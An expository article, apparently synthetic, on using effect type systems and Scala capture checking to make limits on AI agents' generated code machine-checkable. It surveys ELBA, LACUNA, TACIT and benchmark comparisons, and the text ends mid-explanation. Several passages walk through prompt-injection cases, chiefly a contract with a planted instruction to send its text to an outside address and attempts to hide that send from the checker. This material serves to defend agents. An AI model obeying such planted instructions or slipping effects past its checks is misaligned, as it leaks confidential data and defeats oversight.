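# Using effect type systems to make AI agent action guarantees machine checkable

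## Effects, types and agent harnesses

An effect type system is the part of a programming language that lists the outside actions each piece of a program may take. An ordinary type describes a function's data, for example that it takes an integer and returns a string. An effect type also lists what the function may do, such as read a file, send a message or overwrite a stored value, and a compiler checks the list before the program runs. Programming-language researchers developed the idea in the 1980s for code written by people. In 2025 and 2026, several groups applied it to AI agents, which are language models that carry out tasks on a computer. Many agents now act by writing short programs, and a compiler checks these by the same rules as human-written code.

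### What a harness does

A language model only produces text. For that text to have any effect, ordinary software called the *agent harness* has to read it, carry out the action it describes and return the result to the model. *Harness Engineering* (2026), a study of the source code of eleven coding agents, defines an agent as a model plus a harness, where the harness is everything except the model. According to *Natural-Language Agent Harnesses* (2026), the harness determines what the model sees, which tools it may call, how results come back and when the work stops. This sense of "harness" is recent. The term "harness engineering" entered circulation only in February 2026, though programmers were building "test harnesses" well before generative AI, as *What makes a harness a harness* (2026) points out.

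*The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) describes an agent in which the model does the reasoning, while the harness dispatches tool calls, manages input and output, and enforces sandboxing (confining the agent to a closed-off part of the machine). If the model writes "delete the database", nothing happens until the harness acts on it. The harness is therefore the obvious place to check actions, though how good the check can be depends on what the model passes to it.

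In the simplest agents, the model makes one tool call at a time, giving the name of a tool from a fixed list and its arguments. The harness checks the name against the list, runs the tool, returns the result and waits for the next call. In other agents, the model writes a *generated program*, code that combines many operations with loops, conditions and calculations, and the harness runs all of it. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) compares the two approaches on building bibliographies from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. To find the earliest paper on a topic with single tool calls, the model has to look through the entries one by one, whereas a program can sort them. On 100 bibliography tasks, a tool-calling agent used about four times as many model calls and 65 times as many input tokens (the units of text a model reads) as the paper's program-writing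 agent. The two agents had different search tools, so programs may not explain the whole difference.

A program can do far more than the list of tools suggests. If the bibliography agent writes ordinary Python, it can skip the approved function for adding an entry, call the standard library's file-writing function directly and save a citation it made up. Even with a fixed tool list, inputs and outputs reveal little about behaviour. *ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) cites a report from a user of OpenAI's coding agent Codex, in which a sub-agent told to do a read-only code review called an image generator and saved an unrelated picture outside the project. The project's files were unchanged, so anyone who checked only those would have concluded that the sub-agent had followed its read-only instructions.

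### Effects, and when to check them

An *effect* is anything a program does besides computing its result, such as reading a stored value or writing a file. Evaluating 7 + 12 has no effects. A *pure function* is one whose type permits no effects.

The designer partly chooses what counts as an effect, as calls to a language model show. *λ_A* (2026), a small formal language for composing agents, comes with a proposal to mark every model call as an effect of its own. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) instead lets an agent use a second model for summaries and gives that model the type of a pure function. This is reasonable as long as the summarising service keeps no memory between requests, but the compiler cannot check this, so the people who build the harness have to ensure it.

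A *type* is a description of a piece of code that a compiler can verify by fixed rules. A *static* check inspects only the text of the code, before it runs. A *run-time* check monitors the code as it executes and stops it at a forbidden step. Static checking covers every input, but it can reject code that would never take a forbidden step. *A Theory of Gradual Effect Systems* (Bañados Schwerter, Garcia and Tanter, 2014) gives the example of a function that writes to memory if a variable y is true and otherwise returns 1. The function's type has to include the write, even if the programmer knows that y is false, so a caller that forbids writes will reject it. Effect types are therefore said to over-approximate. A run-time check would allow that call, but by the time such a check stops a program, the earlier steps have already happened.

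An agent's generated program does not exist until the agent is already at work, so a static check on it happens during the agent's session, but still before the program takes any action. *LACUNA* (2026) describes a system in which a Scala program leaves a gap for a model to fill during execution. When the model's code arrives, the compiler checks it by the same static rules as handwritten code, before any of it runs.

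### The judgment and its rules

Effect systems rest on one kind of statement, which logicians call a judgment:

Γ ⊢ e : τ ! ε

It means that under the assumptions Γ, the program e has type τ and effects at most ε. The assumptions are the types of the names that e may use. The *effect row* ε is the set of effects that e may perform. The row is an upper bound, so some of its effects may never occur.

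A few rules compute the row from the program's text. The rules below are simplified from ETAS, Tan and colleagues' language for agent systems. The word "perform" marks a request for an outside action, and "let x = e₁ in e₂" runs e₁, names the result x, then runs e₂.

```
Operation   If op takes a τ₁ and returns a τ₂, and v has type τ₁:
            perform op(v)  :  τ₂ ! {op}

Sequence    If e₁ : τ₁ ! ε₁, and e₂ : τ₂ ! ε₂ assuming x : τ₁:
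            let x = e₁ in e₂  :  τ₂ ! ε₁ ∪ ε₂

Branch      If b is true-or-false, e₁ : τ ! ε₁ and e₂ : τ ! ε₂:
            if b then e₁ else e₂  :  τ ! ε₁ ∪ ε₂

Function    If e : τ₂ ! ε assuming x : τ₁:
            fun x ↦ e  :  (τ₁ →ε τ₂) ! ∅

Call        If f : τ₁ →ε τ₂ and v : τ₁:
            f(v)  :  τ₂ ! ε
```

An operation contributes itself as an effect. A sequence contributes the effects of both parts because both will run. A branch also contributes the effects of both sides, because the checker cannot determine which side will run.

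Defining a function has no effects, so the definition has the empty row ∅. The function's type records the effects of the body on its arrow, and calling the function adds them to the caller's row. Because the effects are part of the type, the system can track them when a program puts the function in a list, passes it to another function or returns it from a third, even if the eventual call is far from the definition. A checker that instead traced which function calls which would often fail on such programs, because nobody can work out the full call graph in advance.

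After computing the row ε, the checker passes the program if ε ⊆ A, where A is the set of permitted effects, usually fixed by the developer of the harness. The checker applies the same test to functions that a program passes to other functions. Bañados Schwerter and colleagues give the example of a function h that accepts only arguments with effects in {read, alloc}, where alloc means reserving memory. A function with the row {read} can be passed to h, but one with {write} cannot.

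The row is useful as a guarantee only if it reliably limits what the program does when it runs. *Soundness* is the theorem that if the checker accepts a program with the row ε, no run of that program ever performs an effect outside ε. Bauer and Pretnar (2013), in *An Effect System for Algebraic Effects and Handlers*, prove it in two parts for the core of a research language named Eff. The first part, progress, shows that a well-typed program has either finished, can take another step, or is requesting an operation on its row. The second part, preservation, shows that each step leaves the program's type and row valid for whatever remains to run. Applied at every step, the two parts cover an execution of any length, including one that never ends. Bauer and Pretnar also wrote the proof out in Twelf, a system in which a computer verifies each inference.

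### A contract summary, worked by hand

Odersky and colleagues use the case of an agent that compares confidential contracts and writes up what has changed. A smaller version is enough to show the rules at work. The program reads one contract, asks a model to summarise it and writes the summary to a file:

```
let text    = perform Docs.read("contract") in
let summary = perform Model.ask("Summarise this contract.", text) in
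perform Out.write(summary)
```

Here a model call counts as an effect. The checker checks single operations first, then the larger pieces of code that contain them. Actions that return nothing of interest have the type "unit".

| Piece of the program | Rule | Type and row |
|---|---|---|
| the read | operation | string ! {Docs.read} |
| the request to the model | operation | string ! {Model.ask} |
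| the write | operation | unit ! {Out.write} |
| second and third lines together | sequence | unit ! {Model.ask, Out.write} |
| the whole program | sequence | unit ! {Docs.read, Model.ask, Out.write} |

Suppose the developer permits exactly A = {Docs.read, Model.ask, Out.write}. The harness runs the program because its row is a subset of A (here they are equal).

Now suppose that the contract contains a planted instruction to mail a copy to an outside address, and the model falls for it. The next program it writes has an extra line, perform Net.send(text), just before the write. The operation rule gives that line the row {Net.send}, and the sequence rule carries it up to the top:

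ε = {Docs.read, Model.ask, Net.send, Out.write}

ε \ A = {Net.send}

The difference is not empty, so ε ⊄ A and the checker rejects the program before it reads the contract or does anything else. A run-time check on the network would also have blocked the message, but only after the program had read the contract and passed it to the summarising model.

Rewriting the program does not get the send past the checker. If the model puts the send inside a condition, such as "if the summary is longer than a million words", the branch rule still adds Net.send to the row. If it puts the send inside a function, notify = fun s ↦ perform Net.send(s), then notify has the type string →{Net.send} unit, and calling it adds Net.send to the row. A program that defines notify but never calls it passes, correctly, because it never sends anything.

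The row {Docs.read, Model.ask, Out.write} doesn't specify what the program writes or the order of its operations. It would be the same if the program wrote the full contract into the output file, or wrote the file before reading the contract. Rules about order need an additional mechanism, the trace contract. The row does distinguish this output file from other files, but only because it lists Out.write and not a general File.write. In Eff, each operation carries the name of the particular resource it acts on. Bauer and Pretnar show that if a reference might point to either of two memory cells, the row has to list the operations on both.

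### Where effect rows came from

David Gifford and John Lucassen proposed effect typing at MIT in 1986, with parallel computing rather than security in mind. In his thesis under Gifford, *Types and Effects*, Lucassen (1987) wanted compilers to find the parts of a program that could safely run in parallel, which requires knowing which parts interfere with each other's memory. He gave every expression a type and an effect, and described effects by the region of memory they touch. He already used an exclamation mark for the effect of an expression and promised "machine-verifiable" specifications of side effects. Talpin and Jouvelot (1992), in *Polymorphic type, region and effect inference*, then showed how a compiler can infer both types and effects, so programmers don't have to write them out.

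Monads are another way to record effects in types, and they give much the same result as effect systems. In the late 1980s Eugenio Moggi proposed giving a computation that produces an A its own type, T A, separate from the type of a finished A. Haskell works this way. A value of type Int is an integer and involves no input or output, while IO Int is a computation that may read files or use the network before it yields an integer. Zhou and colleagues use this distinction for an AI calculator. The model has to return a program of type Int, so a program that first runs a command to delete the server's files has the wrong type and is never run. *The Marriage of Effects and Monads* (1999) showed how closely the two approaches are related by adapting Talpin and Jouvelot's effect system directly to monads.

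Haskell's IO is a coarse label, though, because it covers both reading one file and wiping the disk. In the early 2000s, Gordon Plotkin and John Power described effects more finely, by the individual operations that cause them, such as get and set for memory or read and write for a terminal. *Handling Algebraic Effects* (Plotkin and Pretnar, 2013), which extends a 2009 conference paper, added handlers, the subject of the next few paragraphs.

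Most of the later work uses a form of row that owes a lot to the language Koka. *Koka* (Leijen, 2014) starts with a function that squares a number. Its inferred type is int → total int, where "total" means no effects. Adding a line that prints the number changes the inferred type to int → io int, without any annotation from the programmer. Koka's rows can be closed, like ⟨exn, div⟩ for a function that may throw an exception or run forever, or open, like ⟨exn | μ⟩, where μ stands for further effects that depend on the context. Open rows make it possible to give general-purpose helpers a sensible type. The function map, which applies another function to every item in a list, has the same effects as that function, so its type repeats μ. If an agent's program maps notify over a list of contracts, μ becomes Net.send and the subset check fails as before.

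Leijen mentions as a drawback that the only way to forbid an effect in Koka is to write a closed row of everything that remains allowed, which makes code less modular. This is a nuisance for ordinary programmers, but someone confining an agent would more or less want a complete list of permitted actions anyway, with everything else excluded.

### How a handler removes an effect

In languages with handlers, a program that performs an operation issues a request and pauses instead of carrying out the operation itself. A *handler* is a block of code around the program that intercepts certain requests and defines what they mean. A familiar special case is the exception handler, which catches an error and does something else. The handlers of Plotkin and Pretnar extend this to every operation and receive the rest of the paused program as a function, so they can supply an answer and let the program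 continue. Requests that a handler does not cover pass outwards to the next one, as *No value restriction is needed for algebraic effects and handlers* (2016) explains, until a handler takes them or they reach the top level. In an agent, the top level belongs to the harness.

The rule for the row follows from this. If a program has the row ε, and a handler intercepts the operations H and has effects ε_h of its own, the two together have the row

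(ε \ H) ∪ ε_h

An example from Bauer and Pretnar uses both halves of the formula. A program looks up a stored number, writes it back and returns the number plus one, so its row is {lookup, update}. The handler supplies 1 for every lookup and discards every update. When the program finishes, the handler performs one update with the program's result, 2. The handler therefore removes both of the program's effects, but its own final step adds update back, so the combined row is {update}.

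If a handler for the contract program receives Out.write, does nothing and lets the program continue, the resulting row is ({Docs.read, Model.ask, Out.write} \ {Out.write}) ∪ ∅ = {Docs.read, Model.ask}. This is a dry run, and the type shows that it writes nothing. Agent tools that implement dry runs by hand do sometimes get them wrong. Tan and colleagues cite a user of the coding tool aider who wanted to see a patch before applying it. The option for showing differences changed the files, and adding the dry-run option produced no patch. A handler also cannot hide an effect that it performs itself. If it asks a person to confirm each Net.send and then sends the message, ε_h contains Net.send, so the effect stays in the row.

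When a dry-run handler absorbs a write, the write no longer appears in the row. The row is therefore not enough to check rules that cover requests as well as outcomes, so ETAS keeps a separate record of requests.

### What makes the guarantee machine-checkable

The model's prompt can include the instruction "never send the contract to anyone", but no procedure can establish that the model will follow it. Testing the agent on a thousand contracts shows only how it behaved on those thousand. A machine-checkable guarantee needs a property exact enough to prove, a checker that decides by fixed rules whether a program has that property, and a *trusted base*, which is everything that must work correctly for the checker's result to hold in practice. In the contract example, the property is "every effect of this program is in A", and the checker applies the rules above and one subset test.

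The main attraction of the method is that the model is outside the trusted base. In their soundness theorem, Zhou and colleagues treat the model as an arbitrary function that may return any program. Every property the programming language enforces for well-typed programs then holds for the agent's code, provided each generated program passes the type checker before it runs. The threat model of Odersky and colleagues likewise allows for a cloud-hosted model that cooperates fully with an attacker.

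This approach still requires trusting a fair amount of software. For their system, TACIT, Odersky and colleagues list the Scala 3 compiler, the library through which the agent's code reaches files and the network, the runtime that executes the code, and, where the developer uses one, a local model that processes classified text. The library deserves particular suspicion. The checker assumes that Out.write writes to one file. If Out.write also uploaded a backup copy to a server, the contract program would have the same row and pass the same subset test, but it would send the summary over the network every time it ran.

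## Checking an agent's program before it runs

### An expected type for every program

The contract example assumed a harness that gets hold of each program before it runs. Zhou and colleagues built one, a Haskell library called ELBA, in which the whole check sits inside a single function:

```
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

The double colon means "has the type". Defs is the set of functions and types that the model may use, Prompt is the request in ordinary language, and t is whatever type of result the developer wants. Developers can write this type out, but Haskell often infers it from the surrounding code. For example, if a developer runs an agent over a list of messy date strings and then sorts the results with a function that compares dates, the compiler infers that the agent must return a date. ELBA passes that type to the model, so the prompt can be as short as "parse this".

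When the developer's program reaches an agent call, ELBA goes through these steps:

1. It sends the model the prompt, the permitted definitions and the expected type, and asks for exactly one Haskell expression of that type.
2. The compiler checks the expression against the type.
3. If the expression fails, ELBA returns the compiler's error message to the model, which writes a corrected version for the compiler to check again.
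4. If the expression passes, the Haskell interpreter runs it, and the result becomes the value of the agent call.

ELBA retries only after type errors. At that point nothing has run, so a new attempt can't repeat an action. If a program passes the check but crashes partway through, for example because a website is down, it may already have written to a file, and ELBA does not request a new program.

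The expected type does the job that the permitted set A did in the contract example. For the AI calculator described earlier it is Int, which is why Zhou and colleagues consider the calculator safe to put on a public website, where anyone might ask it to delete the server's files. (Standard Haskell has a function that strips off the IO type. Developers can close that gap by compiling the model's code as Safe Haskell, a subset of the language that leaves such functions out.)

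A program that mentions the delete command without running it can still have the type Int, but this is harmless. Zhou and colleagues list exceptions among the effects that Int forbids, but in Haskell a division by zero has the type Int, and so does a calculation that never finishes. A hostile user can't reach the server's files through the calculator but might still keep the server busy with an endless calculation.

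### A bibliography without invented papers

Most agents need some effects, and IO would permit all of them at once. For the bibliography agent, Zhou and colleagues therefore define a new effect type, BibIO, with three operations. In simplified form they are:

```
dblpSearch      :: String      -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI         -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
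```

The first operation searches the DBLP database and returns a list of DOIs, the permanent identifiers of papers. The second fetches the full entry for one DOI, and the third adds an entry to the bibliography file. The empty brackets mean that an operation returns no useful value. The developer sets the expected type of the agent's program to BibIO, which works much like a permitted set of three effects but is coarser than an effect row, because a program that only searches also has a BibIO type.

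To add the earliest paper on a topic, the model might write:

```
do hits    <- dblpSearch "differential privacy"
   entries <- mapM dblpFetchBib hits
   appendToBibFile (minimumBy (comparing year) entries)
```

The second line fetches an entry for every search result, and the third picks the entry with the earliest year. The third line does this with ordinary Haskell functions that have no effects, so the developer doesn't have to anticipate this step and provide a tool for it.

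BibIO alone would not keep invented papers out. If appendToBibFile accepted ordinary text, the model could make up a citation and pass it in. The type Trusted closes this route. It is an *abstract data type*, meaning that the library hides the function that builds values of the type. Outside the library, the only way to get a Trusted Bib is to call dblpFetchBib. The model's program can read entries, sort them and drop some of them, but it can't create or alter one. The compiler rejects each obvious attempt to get around this:

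| What the model writes | Why it fails |
|---|---|
| `writeFile "refs.bib" "@article{...}"` | writeFile has an IO type, and the program needs a BibIO type |
| `appendToBibFile "@article{...}"` | the argument is a String and not a Trusted Bib |
| `appendToBibFile (Trusted madeUpEntry)` | the function that builds Trusted values is not available |

The type records where an entry came from but not whether it belongs in the bibliography, so a real paper on the wrong subject would pass the check.

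On the 100 bibliography tasks mentioned earlier, with Anthropic's Sonnet 5 as the model, the agent wrote 925 citations, and none had a wrong author, year or DOI. The tool-calling agent, which searched the web and wrote out its citations itself, got 19 of 1,002 wrong. The types guarantee the error-free result as long as DBLP's records are correct, so it should hold for a much weaker model too. Zhou and colleagues point out that a tool-calling agent would be just as safe without a type system if its only writing tool fetched an entry from DBLP and saved it in one step. However, that agent couldn't sort and filter entries with code.

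### Why sub-agents inherit the limits

A model that writes its whole program at once must choose the steps before it has seen any data. A person compiling a bibliography would look at the first few search results and perhaps change the search terms. ELBA allows this kind of adjustment by letting a generated program call `agent`. In Zhou and colleagues' example, the program runs a search and stops if it finds nothing. Otherwise it fetches the first entry, adds it to a new prompt and calls `agent` with that prompt as its last step. The sub-agent can then refine the search or write to the file. Repeated calls produce the usual agent loop, in which the model acts, reads the result and acts again.

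The type expected at the point where a parent calls a sub-agent limits what the sub-agent can do. Every step of a BibIO program must have a BibIO type, so Haskell infers BibIO as the expected type of the sub-agent's program too, and the compiler checks that program as strictly as its parent. The parent can grant fewer permissions, for example by asking for a plain String, which allows the sub-agent no effects. If the parent tries to grant more by making a call with the expected type IO, the compiler rejects the parent's program before the sub-agent exists, because that call doesn't fit inside a BibIO program, just as writeFile doesn't. A model that follows malicious instructions in a web page therefore can't start a sub-agent with wider permissions than its own.

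ELBA's types leave out model calls. An agent call sends its prompt to a model, usually over the network, but its type shows no effect, so even a program of type Int can make such calls. A developer who wants to keep some data from the model's provider has to control what goes into the prompts by other means.

### The theorem and its condition

Zhou and colleagues state their soundness theorem for any typed language L. Let traces(e) be the set of all sequences of outside actions that the program e can produce. A property P of such sets is a *type system property* for the type t if it holds for every program of that type:

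⊢ e : t  implies  P(traces(e))

For the type BibIO, P could be "every entry written to disk came from DBLP". Let L_agent be L with the function agent added. The theorem is that every type system property for L is also a type system property for L_agent.

The proof turns a program with agent calls into one without them. It replaces each call with ordinary L code that queries the model, type-checks the answer and evaluates it if it passes. The answer may contain further agent calls, so these must be replaced too. The process ends because each call carries a limit on how deeply agents may nest. The limit drops by one at each level, and a call whose limit is zero returns nothing. The resulting program is in L and has the same type and traces as the original. P holds for every program in L of that type, so it holds for this one and therefore for the original.

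The argument works only if the code around the agent calls is also a typed program in L, which Zhou and colleagues call the most important difference between their approach and earlier ones. Suppose a developer uses ELBA to get a summary of a research field as a String and then has a Python script paste the summary into the bibliography file. The agent's code passes every check, but the file now contains text that didn't come from DBLP. Untyped code that handles retries or decides which agent to call next could cause the same problem.

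The theorem also takes the properties of L as given, so the three library functions behind BibIO remain part of the trusted base.

### All-or-nothing rejection in LACUNA

The Scala system in *LACUNA* has a similar function, `agent[T](task)`, where `T` is the expected type. Each call is a *typed hole*, a gap in a program whose type is already known. LACUNA compiles the model's code at the position of the hole, so the code can use every variable and function available there. The prompt therefore includes the nearby source code, with a marker at the hole, and a list of the available names and their types.

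This is awkward to build in Scala, which normally compiles source code once, before the program runs, and then discards most information about local names. LACUNA adds an operation to the Scala compiler that saves the surrounding source text and the current values of the variables at each agent call. When the model's answer arrives, the system inserts it into the saved text, runs the same compiler on the result with the same settings, and loads the compiled code into the running program. This avoids having to trust a separate checker for generated code. The system correctly handled all of about 400 test cases, which were written without any model and each pair host code with a valid or invalid snippet.

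The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of generated code as a whole. *LACUNA* illustrates this with a variable named balance that holds 100. The program calls agent[Int] with the task "subtract 50 and return the new balance", and the model answers with two lines:

```
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The last line produces text, but the hole requires an integer, so the compiler rejects both lines and balance is still 100. A Python harness that ran the code without checking it first would subtract 50 before discovering that the result was text instead of an integer. If it then asked the model to try again, the second attempt would subtract another 50 and leave a balance of zero.

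This protection applies to one piece of generated code at a time. LACUNA fills a hole only when execution reaches it. If accepted code subtracts 50 and then makes a nested agent call for which the model never produces valid code, the subtraction has already happened. Accepted code that crashes partway also leaves its earlier effects in place. When the retries run out, LACUNA raises an error with the compiler's last messages, and the developer's program can catch it and do something else.

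An ELBA sub-agent gets only its instructions and one string of data, whereas a nested LACUNA call can use everything the outer code has computed so far. That access helps with long tasks, but a developer who wants to keep something from a nested agent has to put the call in a separate function and pass in only what the agent should see.

### TACIT behind a standard tool interface

With both ELBA and LACUNA, developers write the agent application in the typed language. TACIT, which comes from largely the same group as LACUNA, works with existing agents, including coding agents such as Claude Code and GitHub Copilot, without modification. Odersky and colleagues built it as a server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools. The server gives agents a handful of tools, and the important ones accept Scala code as their argument.

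These tools use a compiler, a session and a library. An agent typically asks for a description of the library, opens a session and submits a snippet. The compiler checks the snippet, the session runs it if it passes, and the server returns the output or the error message. The session keeps definitions, so a later snippet can use a variable from an earlier one, and the compiler checks the new snippet against the types of everything already defined.

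A snippet can reach files, other programs or the network only through the library. To read files, it must request access to one folder and read them inside the block of code that follows. Paths outside the folder cause an error at run time, while the compiler tracks the permission in the types and rejects code that would keep it after the block ends. The reusable part of the system is about 1,000 lines of Scala. For a new domain, such as an airline's booking tools, a developer adds a few hundred lines that mostly restate the existing tool descriptions as Scala types.

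TACIT does not meet the condition of Zhou and colleagues' theorem, because the compiler checks only the agent's Scala snippets and the rest of the agent is untyped. The README of lampepfl's *TACIT* on GitHub therefore recommends switching off the agent's built-in shell, file and web tools. An agent with shell access can delete files without sending any Scala to the compiler.

In the paper, the compiler's "safe mode" forbids language features that would defeat the check. According to the README, the released software instead uses a separate filter that searches the code for forbidden patterns, as a stopgap until the project can move to the official safe mode. The filter misses any unsafe code that its list of patterns doesn't cover.

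### The cost to task performance

Writing typed code is harder than filling in the arguments of a tool call, so agents might fail more often when they have to do it. The TACIT and LACUNA teams both tested this against ordinary tool calling with the same models. The table gives the share of tasks solved:

| System | Model | Benchmark | Tool calls | Typed code |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| TACIT | gpt-oss-120b | τ²-bench, airline | 43.8% | 45.2% |
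| TACIT | gpt-oss-120b | τ²-bench, retail | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| TACIT | MiniMax M2.5 | τ²-bench, airline | 58.4% | 61.0% |
| TACIT | MiniMax M2.5 | τ²-bench, retail | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| TACIT | DeepSeek V3.2 | τ²-bench, airline | 57.8% | 58.6% |
| TACIT | DeepSeek V3.2 | τ²-bench, retail | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| TACIT | MiniMax M2.5 | SWE-bench Lite | 43.3% | 41.7% |
| LACUNA | DeepSeek V4 Flash | τ²-bench, four domains | 90.0% | 76.0% |
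| LACUNA | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | τ²-bench, four domains | 33.2% | 29.1% |

In τ²-bench, the agent plays a customer-service representative who talks to a simulated customer and changes orders or bookings. Odersky and colleagues ran every task ten times. One version of the agent called the tools directly, and the other had a single tool for running Scala, with the original tools available as Scala functions. The Scala version did better in all six comparisons, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. The airline domain has 50 tasks, so the smallest gain amounts to only four more successes in 500 runs, but six results in the same direction are harder to attribute to chance.

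Odersky and colleagues credit the gains to the structured data that the Scala functions return and to the compiler's error messages. They may be right, but the Scala agents could also combine several calls in one program. Because no third group of agents wrote code without a type check, the experiment can't separate the benefit of types from the benefit of writing code. It also did little to test how agents work under restrictions, since the airline and retail functions exchange plain data and the signatures in the paper's appendix mention no capabilities.

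In SWE-bench Lite, an agent has to write fixes for 300 real software problems from GitHub. MiniMax M2.5 solved 125 of them with TACIT and 130 with the ordinary tools of the coding agent OpenCode. Odersky and colleagues suspect that the work depends on shell habits that are awkward to express through their library. *Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026), the conference version of the TACIT paper, reports "no significant loss in task performance", which seems fair for these models and tasks.

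LACUNA's results are worse than its paper makes them sound. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, it solved 76.0% of 392 τ²-bench tasks, while the paper's table shows the tool-calling agent solving 90.0%, or roughly 55 more tasks. The text nevertheless describes the two as "on par". Each task ran only once, but a gap that large is unlikely to be chance. It was widest in retail, where LACUNA solved 58.8% and the tool-calling agent 80.9%. The compiler also rejected 22.4% of the code DeepSeek V4 Flash wrote for retail tasks, while TACIT's agents had to retry at most 1.57% of their retail snippets. That comparison is rough because the two teams used different models. However, TACIT lets a model write some code, read the output and write more, whereas LACUNA also requires it to program its own control flow in typed code, which could account for much of LACUNA's lower success rate.

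The other LACUNA comparison is less informative because Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite failed most tasks either way. It scored only four points lower overall than it did with tool calls. In the telecom domain, the compiler rejected 89% of its code, and the agent solved 14.9% of the tasks, compared with 15.8% with tool calls.

*LACUNA* also tests its system on BrowseComp-Plus, a set of 830 hard research questions about a fixed collection of about 100,000 documents. The generated code could call two functions, one to search the collection and one to open a document. DeepSeek V4 Flash answered 27.1% of the questions correctly. The compiler rejected 8.6% of the model's code, which led to an average of 0.7 retries per question, and two-thirds of the questions needed none. *LACUNA* concludes that the type check doesn't reduce accuracy, but the experiment can't support that because it included no agents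 that skipped the type check.

None of these task comparisons involved a leading model. *LACUNA* says that it used smaller, cheaper models on purpose, and the models in the TACIT tests were well behind the strongest available by late 2026. The comparisons show that a middling model can write typed Scala for customer-service work without doing worse than it does with plain tool calls, provided that the harness keeps the familiar loop of acting and reading results. A leading model would probably make fewer coding mistakes, but it would also do better with plain tool calls, so the gap between the two could be wider or narrower. The tests also gave agents the functions that their tasks needed, so they measure the effect of writing typed code, not the effect of strict permissions.

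### Retries and running time

Across TACIT's τ²-bench runs, between 0.32% and 7.93% of snippets needed a retry, depending on the model and domain. These usually passed after one or two retries. The recurring errors that Odersky and colleagues describe were ordinary Scala mistakes. Agents forgot that a value might be missing, or wrote a price as "$50" inside a text template, where Scala treats the dollar sign as the start of a variable name. On tasks like these, the retry rate mostly measures how well a model knows Scala. *LACUNA* suggests that models find Scala harder than Python because their training data contains less of it.

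Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA with stronger models (Opus 4.7, Opus 4.8, Sonnet 5 and GPT 5.4) on AgentDojo, a benchmark of everyday office tasks with planted attacks. ELBA needed an average of 0.13 retries per run, and retries took up 3.4% of the running time. In 7 of 2,688 runs, the model used up its retries without producing a program that passed.

The compiler adds little delay. Once warmed up, Scala checks a typical TACIT snippet in less than a second, far less time than the model takes to respond. Extra model calls add more delay. On AgentDojo, ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL, a 2025 system in which the model writes a single program at the start. Zhou and colleagues attribute the difference mainly to ELBA's sub-agents, which call the model again whenever a program's next step depends on examining data.

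## Tracking permissions as values in the program

TACIT and LACUNA both rely on the Scala compiler to limit what generated code can do. Scala tracks *capabilities* rather than effect rows. A capability is an unforgeable value that a program must hold to perform an effect. In the contract example, where the effect row listed operations such as Docs.read, a capability system would instead give the program an object, docs, and only code that holds this object could read the contracts.

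### Acting only through references

In most programming languages, any line of code can try to open any file by name. The operating system checks whether the user may open the file, and every part of the program has the same rights as that user. In 1966, Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn proposed instead that a program should need an unforgeable token for each resource it uses. Operating systems from Hydra in the 1970s to Google's Fuchsia have adopted the idea.

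Mark Miller's 2006 dissertation, *Robust Composition*, set out the version for programming languages, the *object-capability model*. In this model, the token is an ordinary object reference. A reference to a file object lets code call the object's write method. The file's path is only text, so code that has the path but no reference can't open the file. Miller's language E and Joe-E, a security-oriented subset of Java, both work this way.

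A harness built on this approach could pass the contract program `docs` and `out`, but no network object. If the language model followed the planted instruction to mail the contract, its program would have no way to send it.

A problem arises when a program needs the network for one step but must keep it away from another. Suppose the program passes a function called tidy to a helper that applies it to every contract. If the program defined tidy at a point where it held a network object, tidy may have kept a reference to that object. (A function that keeps references from where it was defined is called a *closure*.) The ordinary type of tidy, from string to string, is the same whether or not it kept the reference. E and Joe-E enforce capabilities only at run time, as Odersky and colleagues point out, so whoever writes the helper can't require a function that holds no network reference.

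### Capture sets

*Capture checking*, an experimental feature of Scala 3, adds those references to the type. A *capturing type* has the form T^{x₁, …, xₙ}, where T is an ordinary type and the part in braces, the *capture set*, lists the capabilities that a value of this type may use. Like an effect row, the set is an upper bound. Functions have a shorter notation that puts the set on the arrow:

| Type | Capabilities the function may use |
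|---|---|
| `String -> Unit` | none, so the function is pure |
| `String ->{out} Unit` | out |
| `String ->{out, net} Unit` | out and net |
| `String => Unit` | any |

The compiler works out the set from the function's body. For example, `(s: String) => out.write(s)` uses out, so its type is `String ->{out} Unit`. A function with a smaller set can stand in for one with a larger set, which in Scala's notation makes it a subtype:

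```
String -> Unit  <:  String ->{out} Unit  <:  String ->{out, net} Unit  <:  String => Unit
```

This is the subset test from the contract example, applied to individual values instead of whole programs. *What's in the Box* (Xu, Bračevac and colleagues, 2025) describes a further rule for objects built from capabilities. A logger that writes to a file f and to the console is itself a capability, and the compiler treats {logger} as smaller than {f, console}. Wrapping a capability in another object therefore doesn't hide it from the compiler.

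An example adapted from Pham, Bračevac and colleagues (2026), in *Classifying Capabilities*, shows the check at work:

```
def report(docs: DocBase^, net: Network^) =
  def attempt(job: () ->{net} Unit) = job()
  attempt(() => net.send(docs.read("contract")))   // rejected: the job also uses docs
```

The `^` after a type marks a value that may carry any capabilities. `attempt` accepts only jobs that use nothing beyond `net`, so the compiler rejects this job, which also uses `docs`. But if the program first read the contract into an ordinary string and then passed `attempt` a job that sends the string, the compiler would accept it, because a string is not a capability. TACIT adds its `Classified` wrapper to limit where data goes, since capture sets limit only which objects a piece of code can use.

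Types also remove an inconvenience of older capability languages. These languages forbid global objects that carry permissions, since any code could use them, so programmers have to pass every permission from the program's entry point down through each function that needs it. Scala can safely allow a global console, because a function that prints to it has the type `() ->{Console.out} Unit`, and the compiler rejects that function wherever a pure one is required. Scala can also pass capabilities implicitly, so programmers don't have to repeat them in every call.

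### A permission that ends with its block

TACIT grants file access for the length of a block of code. Slightly simplified, the library function looks like this:

```
def requestFileSystem[T](root: String)(block: FileSystem^ => T): T
```

It creates a FileSystem capability for the folder root, passes it to the block, and invalidates it when the block returns. T stands for whatever type of result the block produces. If the block reads a report and returns the text, T is String and the program compiles. Odersky and colleagues give an example of a program that tries to keep the access instead:

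```
val bad = requestFileSystem("/data"): fs =>
  () => fs.access("secret.txt").read()
bad()
```

The block reads nothing. It returns a closure that would read the secret file later, after the permission has ended. The compiler rejects it by the following steps:
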